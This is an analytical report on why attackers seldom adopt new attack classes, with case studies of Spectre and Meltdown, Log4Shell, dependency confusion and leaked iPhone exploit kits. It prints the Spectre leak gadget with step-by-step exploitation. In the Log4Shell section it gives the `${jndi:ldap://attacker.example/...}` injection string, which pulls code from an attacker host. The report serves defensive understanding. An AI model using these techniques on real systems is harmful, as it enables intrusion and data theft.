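One reason for caution about the talk is that an intelligence agency has an interest in playing down its secret methods. Charlie Miller, a former NSA employee well known for hacking Apple devices, asked on Twitter whether people should trust what Joyce said. Schneier thought the information was good. According to eWeek, he suspected that the NSA considered its own techniques too sophisticated for the advice to slow it down much. If so, the agency was holding back better techniques, as the model predicts for an attacker who tries the easier routes first.

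Joyce's claim was also mainly about big corporate networks, which nearly always have an unpatched machine or an employee who will click on a phishing link. An up-to-date phone with a careful owner offers fewer openings, which is one reason governments pay so much for phone exploits.

Other evidence supports him on the main point. Schneier on Security's *Credential Stealing as an Attack Vector* (2016) says that Chinese hackers used stolen credentials to break into the US Office of Personnel Management in 2015. The office held the government's personnel records, which made it a very valuable target for a foreign spy agency, yet the hackers apparently didn't need anything new to get in.

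### Where the model predicts novelty, and where it fails

According to the model, attackers will use new techniques when the target is very valuable, when they can reuse the technique widely, or when the cheap routes are closed. If the company in the worked example changed the password and patched the bug, an attacker who valued the target at $100,000 would give up, but the new technique would be worth using against any target worth more than $625,000, down from $990,000.

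The cost of an attack matters for the sceptical argument because it can explain why known classes dominate, however many unknown ones exist. Even if there were a hundred undiscovered attack classes, all of them effective, most attackers would still use stolen passwords as long as those were cheaper. Breach statistics therefore largely reflect which attacks are cheap, and are weak evidence about what else would work. If new techniques became much cheaper to develop, the mix of attacks could change quickly.

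The model is weakest for attackers who don't want money. Herley restricts his analysis to financially motivated crime and leaves the rest as an open question. Allodi and colleagues try to cover more by letting an attacker's revenue include "kudos on hacker forums". But V in the formula is the same whichever route the attacker takes, and for someone who wants admiration it depends on the route. Logging in with a leaked password earns little admiration, while a new technique may impress people even if the target is worthless. Someone driven by curiosity may be doing it for the months of work themselves, in which case much of c becomes a benefit.

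The model is best read as describing people who care about the result and not about how they get it. It could be extended to other people by counting admiration and enjoyment as part of the payoff, but it would then fit nearly any behaviour and predict very little.

A little historical evidence suggests that motive makes a difference. *Bruce Schneier on attack trends* (kees, 2006) summarises a talk in which Schneier described criminals taking over from hobbyists who wanted boasting rights. Computer worms were becoming quieter and more effective while "losing their cleverness". These are one listener's notes, and the listener pointed out that Schneier worked for a company selling security services. But the change is in the direction the model would predict when attackers start to aim for money.

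Attackers also have to estimate p, V and c, and their estimates can be wrong. Some keep using a method because they already know it. If a government agency already has a team of researchers on salary, developing a new technique costs it little extra, and it may develop several that no single target would justify.

Academic and industry security researchers are rewarded for novelty more directly than anyone else. A researcher who discovers a new attack class gets a publication and perhaps some fame, whether or not a criminal could make money from it. We should therefore expect researchers to find many attack classes that work but that hardly any attackers have a reason to use.

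## Why has so little use of Spectre and Meltdown been observed?

Spectre and Meltdown, two related attack classes, became public in January 2018. Nearly nine years later, nobody appears to have publicly confirmed an attack on a real victim with either one. The defences that vendors rushed out may have prevented attacks, or attacks may have gone unnoticed, since victims would have had trouble detecting them. The alarm may also have been overdone, as sceptics conclude.

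### How the attacks work

Both attacks use the processor's cache, a small memory that holds copies of recently used data. Reading from the cache is measurably faster than from main memory, so a program can work out which data the processor has used recently by timing its own reads.

Kocher, Genkin and colleagues (2018), in *Spectre Attacks*, give this example of code that an attacker can exploit:

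```
if (x < array1_size)
    y = array2[array1[x] * 256];
```

The first line checks that x is a valid position in a list called array1. The second line reads the value at that position and uses it to choose a place in another list, array2. An attacker who can choose x proceeds as follows:

1. The attacker runs the code repeatedly with valid values of x, which trains the processor to expect the check to succeed.
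2. The attacker gets array1_size out of the cache, then supplies an x far beyond the end of array1, so that "position x" is really a secret stored elsewhere in the program's memory.
3. The processor has to fetch array1_size from main memory, which can take several hundred clock cycles. Instead of waiting, it guesses that the check will succeed and runs the second line early.
4. Suppose the secret is the number 84. The second line then reads place 84 × 256 in array2, and the processor puts a copy of that place in the cache.
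5. When array1_size arrives, the check fails and the processor discards the result. The copy stays in the cache.
6. The attacker times a read from each of the 256 possible places. Number 84 is the fast one, so the secret is 84.

The attacker can read the program's memory one byte at a time by repeating this with other values of x. The program has no bug in the usual sense, since the check is present and correct. In a second variant of Spectre, the attacker trains the processor to mispredict where a jump leads, so the processor briefly runs a fragment of the victim's code that the attacker chose.

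Meltdown doesn't require any training. Operating systems used to keep the memory of the kernel, their privileged core, mapped into every program's address space but marked as off limits. *Meltdown* (Lipp, Schwarz and colleagues, 2018) describes an attack in which a program tries to read a kernel address. The processor raises an error, but by then a vulnerable Intel chip has fetched the value and run the next few instructions with it. Those instructions use the value to choose a place in a list, and timing reveals which place, as in Spectre.

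Meltdown let an ordinary program read the kernel's memory, which it should not be able to do. Because the kernel usually has all physical memory mapped, the attacker could read other programs' data too. Spectre could make a correctly written program leak its memory. It also undermined the browser sandbox, which is supposed to make it safe to run code from any website. Kocher and colleagues wrote JavaScript that read the memory of the browser process running it. They got Spectre to work on Intel, AMD and ARM processors, while Lipp and colleagues demonstrated Meltdown on Intel chips.

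### The search for real use

The discoverers' own website, *Meltdown and Spectre*, answers the question of whether anyone had used the flaws against real victims with "We don't know."

Within a month, the testing organisation AV-Test had collected almost 140 files related to the flaws. Some reports called them malware, but AV-Test thought most were proofs of concept. Grooten (2018), in *There is no evidence in-the-wild malware is using Meltdown or Spectre*, looked up some of the files and found names like "MeltdownTest.exe". The files also lacked packing, the layers of disguise that malware authors normally add. The lack of packing is weaker evidence than it seems that the files were not malware. As Grooten notes, a scan for the exploit code would probably miss it inside a packed file, so a search like this was likely to find only unpacked files.

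Another scare came in 2021, when the French researcher Julien Voisin found working Spectre exploits for Windows and Linux on VirusTotal, a website where people upload files to be scanned for malware. The Linux exploit could read the file that holds users' password hashes (scrambled passwords that an attacker can try to crack). The Record's *First Fully Weaponized Spectre Exploit Discovered Online* traced the exploits to Canvas, a commercial tool for penetration testers, who break into systems with the owners' permission. Canvas's maker had advertised a Spectre exploit as early as February 2018. Pirated copies of the tool had circulated in private Telegram channels since at least October 2020, so criminals have probably had access to a working exploit for six years. The Record found no evidence that anyone had used the exploits in an attack.

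CISA does not appear to count either flaw as exploited. GCVE's *CPU处理器内核存在Meltdown漏洞(CNVD-2018-00304)* (2018), a database entry with later updates, includes CISA's assessment of Spectre's first variant from 28 May 2026. It rates exploitation as "none", so that variant is probably not in CISA's catalogue of exploited vulnerabilities. The security company Pentest-Tools lists Meltdown as not in the catalogue in *Missing Linux Kernel mitigations for Meltdown hardware vulnerabilities CVE-2017-5754*.

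Although little use of Spectre and Meltdown has been observed, both score high on EPSS, a statistical model that forecasts whether anyone will try to exploit a given flaw in the next 30 days. CVELogic's *CVE-2017-5753* (2018) shows a score of about 94% for Spectre's first variant, and ManageEngine's *CVE-2017-5754* shows about 88% for Meltdown. These scores don't record observed attacks, and published exploit code probably explains much of them, since CVELogic lists three public exploits for the Spectre variant.

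### What researchers have managed since

Researchers have kept finding new versions of these attacks. *Enter, Exit, Page Fault, Leak* (2025) cites Foreshadow from 2018, ZombieLoad from 2019, Retbleed from 2022 and Inception from 2023. Critics mostly objected that such attacks worked only in the laboratory. According to Kaspersky, earlier research on attacks between virtual machines had assumed that the attacker already had malware on the host, in which case the attacker would hardly need Spectre. Two recent projects avoided that assumption and tested live commercial services.

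The first is *Rain* (Hertogh, Quakkelaar and colleagues), by VUSec, a research group at Vrije Universiteit Amsterdam, with a colleague in Birmingham. Cloud companies rent out virtual machines, and several customers' machines may share one physical computer. The researchers rented machines from Google and Amazon through ordinary accounts and tried to read the memory of other virtual machines on the same computer. They had both companies' permission, and the machines they targeted were their own.

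Hertogh and colleagues combined two flaws that the industry considered harmless by then. L1TF, which researchers discovered in January 2018, lets a virtual machine read whatever is in the first-level cache of the processor core it runs on. Cloud companies had responded by emptying that cache at certain moments and keeping different customers off the same core. But the hypervisor, the software that manages the virtual machines, could still run on the attacker's core. They found a fragment of hypervisor code that resembles the Spectre example above but lacks its second read, so it loads a secret into the cache without revealing it. They then used L1TF to read the secret from the cache.

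On Google's cloud, the attack stole a web server's private encryption key in 25 of 28 attempts, taking 14.2 hours on average. Most of that time was spent finding one address in the host's memory, and reading the key took about 25 minutes. The attack also succeeded in all ten attempts on a machine that the team had deliberately overloaded. It works only on Intel processors of the Skylake generation or older, which clouds still use. On Amazon's cloud, it revealed only non-sensitive data about the host, because Amazon had made customers' memory inaccessible to the hypervisor. Google added a similar defence and paid a bounty of more than $150,000, the most its cloud programme had awarded.

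The other target was Cloudflare Workers, a service that runs small programs for customers on Cloudflare's servers. Thousands of customers' programs can share a process, because they would start more slowly in separate ones. Schwarzl, Xiao and colleagues (2026), in *Remote-Timer-as-a-Service*, used one of their Workers to read a login token from another of their Workers at up to 12 bits per second, with 99% accuracy. Cloudflare freezes the clock available to Workers, so the attacking program timed its reads by sending messages to a clock elsewhere. The Hacker News' *Cloudflare Workers Spectre Attack Leaks JWT From Co-Located Worker at 12 Bits/Second* (2026) adds that the team measured at night, when the processors were 10% to 25% busy. The attack is slower on a busy server but still works.

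| Attack | Setting | Reported rate | Time to read 256 bytes at that rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Meltdown, 2018 | Computers without the patch | Up to 503 KB per second | Half a millisecond |
| Earlier attack on Cloudflare Workers, 2021 | Local test network | 120 bits per hour | 17 hours |
| Rain, disclosed 2025 | Google's cloud | About 1 byte per second | 4 minutes |
| New attack on Cloudflare Workers, 2026 | Live service | Up to 12 bits per second | 3 minutes |

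In September 2026 VUSec disclosed another Spectre attack, Branch Target Reuse. It targets just-in-time compilers, which translate programs into machine code as they run and are built into browsers and the Linux kernel (Kovacs, 2026, *New Spectre v2 Variant Exposes Intel, AMD, Arm CPUs to Data Leaks*). The attack can leak the password hash of a Linux machine's administrator within minutes, according to Underhill (2026), in *New Spectre Attack Leaks Linux Root Password Hash in Minutes*.

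The attacks have become much more practical, at least for experts, but they are still demonstrations, and none involved a real victim.

### Are the attacks too awkward to use?

Spectre and Meltdown only read memory, and the attacker must already be able to run code on the machine. For this reason, Grooten doubted in 2018 that malware would ever make much use of them. A criminal who wants to encrypt a company's files gains little from slowly reading fragments of memory, although a fragment that contains a password can be valuable. Lipp and colleagues write that an attacker also has to tailor Spectre to the victim's software, and that manual work makes the attack hard to use against many victims.

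This explanation is good for ordinary office computers but weak for browsers and clouds, which routinely run strangers' code. In SC Media's *Public clouds threatened by old vulnerabilities*, the Rain researchers agree that regular users have little to fear, but they say the business model of public clouds is "to provide remote code execution as a service".

The slowness of these attacks is a weaker explanation for how little use has been observed than it seems. Meltdown was fast. At its top speed, an attacker could have copied 16 gigabytes of memory in about nine hours. The later attacks are slow partly because of the defences. Cloudflare froze its clocks to make timing difficult, and Rain had to use an indirect method because the defences blocked the direct one.

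### Do attackers have easier routes?

Attackers usually have easier options, and the cost model in the previous section predicts that they will take them. Someone who can already run code on a company's computer can look for a saved password or an unpatched bug that gives full control. Even in the cloud, attackers have ways other than Spectre to read another customer's data. The Hacker News' *Critical PwnEscape Linux Kernel Vulnerability Lets Guest VMs Read Host Memory* (2026) describes a kernel flaw that let a virtual machine read its host's memory in the live service of Vercel, another company that runs customers' code.

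Ordinary criminals have ignored Spectre, probably mainly because they have easier ways to attack, but this does not mean the flaw could do little damage.

### Did early and expensive defences work?

Vendors began work on fixes before the public knew about the flaws. The main defence against Meltdown already existed, because researchers had designed it to stop a different attack on the kernel. According to *A New Doctrine for Hardware Security* (2020), it removes the kernel's memory from each program's address space, so Meltdown cannot read it. Lipp and colleagues urged everyone to deploy it immediately, and the makers of Windows, Linux and OS X had their versions ready to release. The defence slows switching between programs and the kernel, which is why operating systems had previously kept the kernel mapped in every program.

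Spectre was harder to fix. Browser makers first reduced the precision of the clocks that web pages can use. Then they largely gave up on protecting data within a process and put different websites in separate processes. This change, known as site isolation, uses more memory. Operating systems gained thousands of lines of code for choosing the right protection on each processor. Some complete fixes slowed computers so much that hardly anyone adopted them. To stop L1TF fully on an old processor, for example, a cloud company would have to turn off the hardware feature that makes virtual machines fast.

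Cloudflare's *Dynamic Process Isolation* (2021) describes the aim as making attacks harder until they are infeasible, since no complete defence against Spectre is known. If that worked, the explanations overlap, because the defences may be why attackers find Spectre awkward to use and other routes easier.

There is evidence that defences do not fully explain why so little use has been observed. grsecurity's *Cross-Process Spectre Exploitation* presents an attack between real programs and reports that almost no ordinary software uses the available protection against this kind of attack. Chrome was the only exception its author had seen. Many organisations are also slow to patch, so a good number of computers must have stayed vulnerable to Meltdown for months or years after the exploit code came out, yet nobody seems to have reported a wave of attacks on them.

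Even so, these unpatched machines are poor evidence of what would have happened without the patches, because if most machines are patched, the rest may be too few to make an attack tool worth building.

### Would anyone have noticed?

Spectre and Meltdown leave nothing in traditional log files, and their discoverers warned that antivirus software would struggle to distinguish the attacks from normal programs. The Rain team later attacked Google's and Amazon's clouds on and off for several months. Neither company's monitoring detected the attacks, although Google had been watching for certain attacks of this type since 2018.

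Cloudflare's case is similar. In Schwarzl and Pedersen, *A revisit of remote Spectre attacks on Cloudflare Workers*, the company reports no indicators of active exploitation over the previous three years. But its detector missed the researchers' own attack because it isolated a suspicious program only after a run had finished, and the researchers could keep one run going for more than 20 hours. Their program also sent constant messages to an outside clock, which made it look like one that was merely busy communicating. Cloudflare may have had other ways to search, but its finding is weak evidence that nobody had used the same attack earlier.

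Attackers may also have known about Spectre and Meltdown before any defences existed. Three teams independently found Meltdown, and two people independently found Spectre. If that many researchers could find them at about the same time, an intelligence agency could have found them earlier. No evidence has emerged that one did, but an agency's use of them might not have left any.

A careful spy can hide the use of an exploit much better than criminals who use it on a large scale. Criminals who spread malware containing an exploit to thousands of computers leave copies behind, and sooner or later an antivirus company analyzes one. This has happened often enough with other exploits that widespread criminal use of Spectre would very probably have come to light by now.

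### What would settle it

Some kinds of evidence would help to separate these explanations:

- A leaked or captured toolkit that contained a Spectre exploit, with records of its use, would show that secrecy accounts for at least part of the silence.
- Cloud companies could place fake passwords in the memory of virtual machines and store them nowhere else. If someone tried to log in with one, it must have leaked from memory. Several years without such an attempt would count against hidden use, at least on those machines.
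- If early defence is the main reason, attacks should appear where a large and valuable group of machines goes without it. A future flaw of the same type that vendors could not patch for a year would be a good test.
- If easier routes are the main reason, attackers should ignore even undefended machines as long as ordinary bugs and stolen passwords still work on them.
- Prices would also help. A broker who offered a large sum for a reliable Spectre exploit would presumably have a customer who wanted to use it.

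The most likely explanation, for now, depends on the attacker. Ordinary criminals had better options, so they would probably have made little use of either flaw on office computers even without early defences. Those defences probably mattered more in browsers, where a single malicious page could otherwise have tried to read data from millions of visitors who had installed nothing. In clouds, nobody can be very confident that no spy has done what the Rain team did.

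### What the case supports

The sceptic's second premise, that celebrated new attack classes saw little use, holds for Spectre and Meltdown if it refers only to observed use. It is much harder to conclude from this that the flaws were never very dangerous.

Let U be the number of attacks that would have happened if nobody had built any defences. Let d be the share of these that the defences prevented, and q the chance that someone notices and reports an attack that does happen. The expected number of sightings is then

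U × (1 − d) × q

Suppose, with invented figures, that the defences prevented 90% of attacks (d) and that 5% of the remaining attacks were seen (q). Each sighting would then represent 200 attacks in an undefended world. Zero sightings would be compatible with up to about 600 such attacks (U), since at that level we would expect three sightings and would see none about one time in 20. Six hundred attacks over nearly nine years is a small number compared with the 22,000 breaches in a single Verizon report, so the sceptic would be more or less right. But if the defences prevented 99.9% of attacks, zero sightings would be compatible with a U of up to about 60,000. Nobody has measured d, and we can't infer it from low use after the defences were deployed.

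The defences also existed only because researchers found the flaws and told the vendors before publishing. Defenders learned of Spectre and Meltdown in time to prepare, so the two cases provide little evidence about what happens when an attacker discovers a new attack class first.

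## Which new attack classes were widely exploited soon after discovery, and how did they spread?

Attackers began using several other new attack classes within months of the first public description, and defenders learned of one only because attackers were already using it. These cases count against the sceptic's second premise, that attackers rarely use celebrated new classes. The table lists the best-known cases, along with two classes that took years to spread.

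| Attack | First public description | First mass use | Scale |
|---|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | December 1998 | Spring 2008 | Hundreds of thousands of web pages altered |
| Format-string bugs | June 2000, after an isolated report in September 1999 | January 2001 (Ramen worm) | An unknown number of Red Hat Linux servers |
| Reentrancy | Early June 2016 | 17 June 2016 (DAO theft) | One theft of about 3.6 million ether, then worth at least $50 million |
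| Java lookup injection | August 2016 | December 2021 (Log4Shell) | About 400 attempts per second at one company after five days |
| Memcached amplification | November 2017 | February 2018 | A flood of 1.35 terabits per second against GitHub |
| Dependency confusion | February 2021 | February and March 2021 | More than 5,000 imitation packages, few of them openly malicious |
| HTTP/2 Rapid Reset | October 2023 | August 2023 | Up to 398 million requests per second at Google |

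A format-string bug occurs when a program uses a user's text as a template for its output. In C, these templates can contain codes that read memory and one that writes to it. Programmers had made this mistake for decades before someone published a working exploit for WU-FTPD, a popular file server, in June 2000. Researchers then found the same bug in many other programs. Seven months after the exploit was published, the Ramen worm spread by exploiting format-string bugs in three programs that came with Red Hat Linux.

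A thief exploited reentrancy just over a week after developers blogged about the danger. The target was The DAO, an investment fund run by a program on the Ethereum blockchain. When a member withdrew money, the program sent the payment before reducing the member's balance. The recipient could also be a program, and the thief's program responded to each payment by requesting another before the balance had changed. A single theft hardly counts as mass use, but it took about a third of the fund's money. Most Ethereum users later agreed to reverse it.

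The memcached and Rapid Reset attacks both overload a target with traffic. In the memcached attack, the attacker sends a small request to a badly configured database server and forges the return address, so that the server sends an enormous reply to the victim. In Rapid Reset, the attacker opens requests to a web server and immediately cancels them. The server still processes the cancelled requests, but they don't count towards its limit on open requests. Google, Cloudflare and Amazon found the technique by investigating record-breaking attacks in August 2023 and published it that October.

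SQL injection spread much more slowly. Jeff Forristal described it in the hacker magazine *Phrack* in 1998, and criminals used it against individual companies for years. It became a mass attack in 2008, when automated tools began to find vulnerable sites and insert malicious links into their pages.

Not all seven are clearly new classes. Format strings, SQL injection, reentrancy and dependency confusion each introduced a new principle, or one that few defenders had considered. Attackers had been bouncing traffic off other people's servers long before they used memcached, so that attack is closer to a new instance of a known class. Rapid Reset is arguably a new technique for an old kind of flood. On a strict reading, the list covers about 25 years and contains only three new classes that spread within a year.

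### Java lookup injection and Log4Shell

Java programs can look up objects, such as database connections, by name through the Java Naming and Directory Interface (JNDI). The program queries a directory server, which can return either the object itself or a reference to a "factory", the code that builds the object. The server can also include an address from which to download that code.

At the Black Hat conference on 3 August 2016, two researchers at Hewlett Packard Enterprise showed how to abuse this. Muñoz and Mirosh, in *A Journey from JNDI/LDAP Manipulation to Remote Code Execution Dream Land*, describe the attack as follows:

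1. The attacker finds a program that looks up a name a visitor can choose. In place of a name, the attacker supplies the full address of a server that the attacker controls. A full address overrides the server that the programmers had set.
2. The program contacts the attacker's server, which replies with a reference to a factory.
3. The program downloads the factory from the attacker and runs it.

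The idea came from attackers. In 2015, a hacking operation known as Pawn Storm used JNDI to bypass the prompt that asks users for permission before a Java program runs in their browser. Muñoz and Mirosh read an analysis of that malware and saw that the same principle would work against company servers. They named the new class JNDI injection, and eWeek's *HPE Warns of JNDI Java Injection Flaws* (2016) reported it a week later.

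A perfect target already existed. Log4j is a free component that Java programs use to write log files. In July 2013 a volunteer had asked for JNDI lookups in Log4j and supplied the code, which the project accepted. From then on, if a log message contained text such as `${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/x}`, Log4j performed the lookup. Programs constantly log what visitors send them, including the name of the visitor's browser, so an attacker could simply put this text where the browser's name should be. According to *Log4shell*, a paper from the NDSS security symposium, the feature turned a logging system into "a powerful command interpreter". (Prompt injection, an attack on AI models, also gets a system to treat text it was only meant to read as an instruction.)

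An engineer at the Chinese company Alibaba reported the flaw to Log4j's maintainers on 24 November 2021. The maintainers worked on the fix in public, as open-source projects usually do. On 9 December, a Chinese security company posted a partly hidden screenshot of an exploit. *Review of the December 2021 Log4j Event* (2022), by a US government panel called the Cyber Safety Review Board, suggests that the company may have worked out the flaw from a test version of the fix, though the panel couldn't confirm this. The maintainers released the finished patch on 10 December.

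By then attacks had begun. Graham-Cumming and Martinho report in *Exploitation of Log4j CVE-2021-44228 before public disclosure* that Cloudflare saw its first attempt nine minutes after a tweet made the flaw public. Cloudflare blocked 5,483 requests per minute on 10 December and 27,439 per minute on 12 December. Attackers soon learned to disguise the telltale letters "jndi" with Log4j's own functions, such as one that converts text to lower case. They also moved from looking for vulnerable machines to stealing passwords from them.

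Cloudflare had also recorded three probes on 1 December, more than a week before disclosure. These were probably not criminal attacks. The Cyber Safety Review Board reports that a technology company thought similar activity that day looked like someone testing the Alibaba engineer's demonstration. The board examined classified material and industry data and found no evidence that criminals or states had used the flaw before 9 December. Burton, Kim and colleagues, of the security company Infoblox, suspect that bounty hunters had shared the flaw and were collecting rewards for it.

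Attempts to exploit the flaw are a poor measure of harm, because researchers were also scanning the internet for it. Akamai, which carries a large share of web traffic, traced about 57% of the first week's activity to known malicious sources. Ransomware groups, state hackers and the Mirai botnet all used the flaw, but the Cyber Safety Review Board was somewhat surprised to find less exploitation than many experts had predicted. It also warned that nobody collects reliable figures on exploitation. Much of the burden was the work of defending against the flaw. One US government department spent 33,000 hours on this, or about 16 years of one person's working time.

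Log4Shell can support the view that attackers use new classes or the view that they use known ones. It was one of the most widely attempted exploits ever, and its class had been unknown a few years earlier. But JNDI injection had been public for more than five years, so a breach report would rightly have counted Log4Shell as a new instance of a known class. Someone who had checked popular Java components against the 2016 talk could have found the flaw, but apparently neither defenders nor attackers did. The lack of known earlier attacks is better evidence that attackers missed it than it is for Spectre, because a Log4Shell attack normally leaves its text in the victim's logs, though many companies would have deleted those logs after a few months.

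### Dependency confusion

Programmers build software out of packages, which a tool called a package manager downloads and installs. Many companies use both public packages and private ones from an internal server. In February 2021, the researcher Alex Birsan described what can happen if an outsider publishes a package under the name of a company's private one.

The package manager may look for the name in both places. Willison (2021) explains in *10th February 2021* that one setting of pip, the standard package tool for Python, makes it choose the package with the higher version number. If the company's own package is version 3.2, an outsider can publish version 100 and the company's computers will install that instead. In npm, the main package system for JavaScript, a package can also include a script that runs automatically on installation, so the outsider's code runs inside the company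 without anyone clicking on anything.

An attacker needs to know the private names, but companies often reveal them by accident, for example in the code of their websites. Birsan's packages ran inside more than 35 companies, including Apple, Microsoft and Tesla. He earned over $130,000 in bug bounties, which companies pay for reports of flaws.

The spread of this attack is unusually well documented because packages are public and dated. Sonatype (2021), a company that sells protection against malicious packages, found about 150 imitations within 48 hours of the news and raised the count to more than 275 on 13 February. Like Birsan's packages, most only sent back basic details such as the computer's name and network address. Many copied his code, including the comments. One imitator reused the package name that had earned Birsan $30,000 from Shopify.

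The first openly malicious packages appeared about three weeks after the disclosure. Sonatype's *Newly Identified Dependency Confusion Packages Target Amazon, Zillow, and Slack* describes packages that tried to steal the file of password hashes from Linux machines, or the user's command history, which can contain passwords. Some also opened a connection that let the attacker control the machine.

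By early March the number of copycat packages had passed 700, and then nearly 5,000 more appeared, according to Sonatype's *PyPI and npm Flooded With Over 5,000 Dependency Confusion Copycats*. The total exaggerates the danger, since Sonatype's *Why are Dependency Confusion Attacks Not Going Away?* attributes a batch of more than 5,000 to one pseudonymous user who wanted to draw attention to the problem. None of Sonatype's customers appeared to have run the malicious packages from early March, but nobody seems to know how many other companies did.

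The attack still works on companies that haven't changed their settings. Microsoft's *33 malicious npm packages abuse dependency confusion profile developer environments* (2026) describes 33 packages published on 28 May 2026 and 12 more published the next day. They imitated the private packages of several organisations, including the Russian bank Sberbank, and many had the version number 100.100.100. The code only gathered information about each machine, but the attacker could have switched it to do more.

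In April 2024, one of the three accounts behind these packages had published a harmless test labelled as bug-bounty research. Microsoft concludes that a researcher became an attacker, although someone else could have taken over the account.

The attack class was new to most of the industry in 2021, but the people who ran Maven Central, the main public store of Java packages, had seen the danger long before Birsan and guarded against it. Anyone publishing there must prove that they own the internet domain on which the package's name is based, so an outsider can't easily claim a company's name. Sonatype, which manages Maven Central, says it had defended this rule for more than 16 years against users who wanted something easier.

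### The usual stages

A new attack often spreads in four stages. First, someone describes it in a paper or talk. Then someone publishes a *proof of concept*, code that demonstrates the attack. Next, the makers of penetration-testing tools add a reliable version. Finally, criminals build it into a worm, a botnet or a kit that people can use without understanding the attack.

Each stage lowers c in the cost model. With a paper, attackers don't have to discover the attack themselves, and with a proof of concept, they can skip much of the development. Testing tools reduce the skill required and usually raise p. With a kit, attacking one more target takes almost no extra work.

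Publication can greatly change an attacker's choice. In the earlier example, a new technique cost $500,000 to develop and lost $420,000 on a single $100,000 target. If somebody else publishes the technique and adapting it costs only $5,000, the expected gain is $75,000. That is more than the $25,000 from the known bug, so the new technique becomes the best option even for a criminal who would never have paid to develop it.

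JNDI injection passed through the early stages slowly. In 2017, after the 2016 talk, Moritz Bechler published a paper on Java flaws, along with a tool that could act as the malicious directory server. When the Log4j flaw became public, many of the first demonstrations used that tool. The class had been at the second stage for four years by then, which is one reason the last step was so quick.

Attacks can skip stages. Dependency confusion needed no testing tool, because copying Birsan's package and changing its name was enough. Attackers used Rapid Reset on a large scale before it was first described publicly.

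An attack can also stop at one stage. Spectre reached the third stage within about a month, with the Canvas exploit, but criminals still don't appear to have adopted it. Publishing an attack makes it easier to use, but criminals must also want what it provides.

### When finished exploits escape

Criminals sometimes get working exploits that a government paid to develop, and they can adopt them quickly. By most accounts, the NSA developed EternalBlue, an exploit for Windows file sharing. Microsoft patched the flaw on 14 March 2017. A month later, a group calling itself the Shadow Brokers published the exploit, and 28 days after that someone used it in the WannaCry worm. WannaCry encrypted files on more than 200,000 computers in about 150 countries and disrupted British hospitals. EternalBlue relied on memory corruption, a very old kind of flaw, so it was not a new attack class.

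A more recent case involves iPhones. Google Threat Intelligence Group's *Coruna* (2026) traces a kit of 23 exploits through three owners in 2025:

- In February, a customer of a surveillance company was using parts of it against selected targets.
- In the summer, suspected Russian spies hid it in Ukrainian websites, where it attacked selected iPhone users in one region.
- By the end of the year, a criminal group operating from China had put the whole kit on a large number of fake financial websites. These attacked vulnerable iPhones wherever the visitor was and searched them for cryptocurrency wallets.

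The mobile security company iVerify calls this the first observed mass exploitation of iPhones, according to The Hacker News' *Coruna iOS Exploit Kit Uses 23 Exploits* (2026). Nobody has established how the kit changed hands, though Google Threat Intelligence Group suspects a market in second-hand exploits.

Some of Coruna's exploits used techniques that had never been public, so the criminals acquired new methods they can reuse with other flaws, as well as particular vulnerabilities. But the kit worked only on versions of Apple's software up to December 2023. By the time the criminals had it, iPhone owners who installed updates had been safe from it for well over a year.

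A second iPhone exploit chain, DarkSword, spread faster. Google Threat Intelligence Group's *The Proliferation of DarkSword* (2026) describes its use from November 2025 by a group targeting Saudi users and by customers of a Turkish surveillance company. The suspected Russian spies who had used Coruna were using DarkSword by December.

The operators of the Saudi campaign may have bought or been given the code. They added an exploit that did not properly handle version 18.7 of Apple's software, which had been out for two months. Google Threat Intelligence Group infers that someone may have written the update months before the operators obtained or used it. *DarkSword Malware* (Schneier, 2026) reports that a version of DarkSword leaked onto the internet a week after researchers publicly identified it, and then came into broader use.

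Other exploits now pass between groups before defenders have a patch. Charrier and colleagues found that at least two groups, some of them criminal, were using the same zero-day in the file-compression program WinRAR in July 2025. They also think Chinese espionage groups have become better at sharing exploits that a single group would once have kept to itself. Some techniques stay with the states that developed them, and those are the least likely to appear in these accounts.

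### How soon exploitation follows a patch

Researchers have measured the delay before exploitation much better for individual vulnerabilities than for classes. In an early study, *Before We Knew It* (2012), Leyla Bilge and Tudor Dumitraș of Symantec searched records from 11 million computers for malicious files that exploited a flaw before its public disclosure. They found 18 such flaws, 11 of which had not been known to be zero-days. The attacks had gone on for an average of 312 days before disclosure. After disclosure, the number of attacks grew by a factor of up to 100,000.

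The usual measure today is *time to exploit*, the number of days from the release of a patch to the first known exploitation. Mandiant estimated an average of 63 days for 2018 and 2019, and five days for 2023. Kutscher estimates minus seven days for 2025, meaning that exploitation began before the patch was released.

A negative figure means that, on average, exploitation began before the patch existed, but most of the flaws may still not have been zero-days. Suppose attackers exploited one flaw 40 days before its patch and two others 5 and 14 days after theirs. The mean is (−40 + 5 + 14) / 3 = −7, although users could have patched two of the three flaws in time. A few zero-days that attackers used quietly for months can greatly lower the mean.

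The figure also covers only vulnerabilities that somebody exploited, a small minority of those published, and it depends on when investigators think exploitation began. EternalBlue's time to exploit is 59 days if counted from WannaCry, but probably around minus 1,800 days if counted from the NSA's first use, which reportedly came about five years before the leak.

None of this measures how quickly attackers adopt new attack classes. If the attacks of 9 December count as the first, the Log4j flaw was exploited one day before the patch, a time to exploit of minus one day, but 1,954 days after the talk that introduced JNDI injection. A time to exploit of minus seven days is a serious problem for anyone who relies on patching, but it could occur even if attackers never used a new attack class.

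The speed of exploitation affects how breach records classify attacks. Once a new class has been public for a few weeks, anyone recording its victims will count it as known. Dependency confusion was already known when the first password-stealing packages appeared, and reentrancy had only just become known at the time of the DAO theft. A record almost entirely of known classes could therefore include many attacks from classes that defenders had known about for only days.

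### What the fast cases had in common

The attacks that spread quickly differ from Spectre mainly in that attackers can launch them remotely, they work reliably, many targets are vulnerable in the same way, and attackers benefit directly from success.

Criminals probably ignored Spectre mainly because it works only once the attacker's code is running on the victim's machine, while Log4Shell could be exploited remotely by sending a line of text. Heartbleed, a 2014 flaw in widely used encryption software, only let attackers read fragments of memory, as Spectre does, but anyone on the internet could use it against a vulnerable server. Within about a week of its disclosure, someone had used it to steal some 900 people's social insurance numbers from Canada's tax agency. Being limited to reading memory therefore can't be the whole reason that criminals ignored Spectre.

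People can use a reliable attack without understanding it. Charrier and colleagues note that injection flaws often let attackers run code reliably, without the difficult work that memory corruption requires. Attackers could exploit Log4Shell without a password or a mistake by a user. Rain, the attack on Google's cloud, was also reliable but far slower.

JNDI injection was not widely exploited until Log4Shell because earlier targets were too different from one another. In 2016 the attack already worked remotely and gave the attacker full control of a program, but the attacker had to find a suitable lookup in each application separately. Log4j put the same flaw in thousands of products, so one line of text worked on all of them. SQL injection seems to have had a similar history. Each website needed its own attack until criminals automated the work, and then the number of victims jumped.

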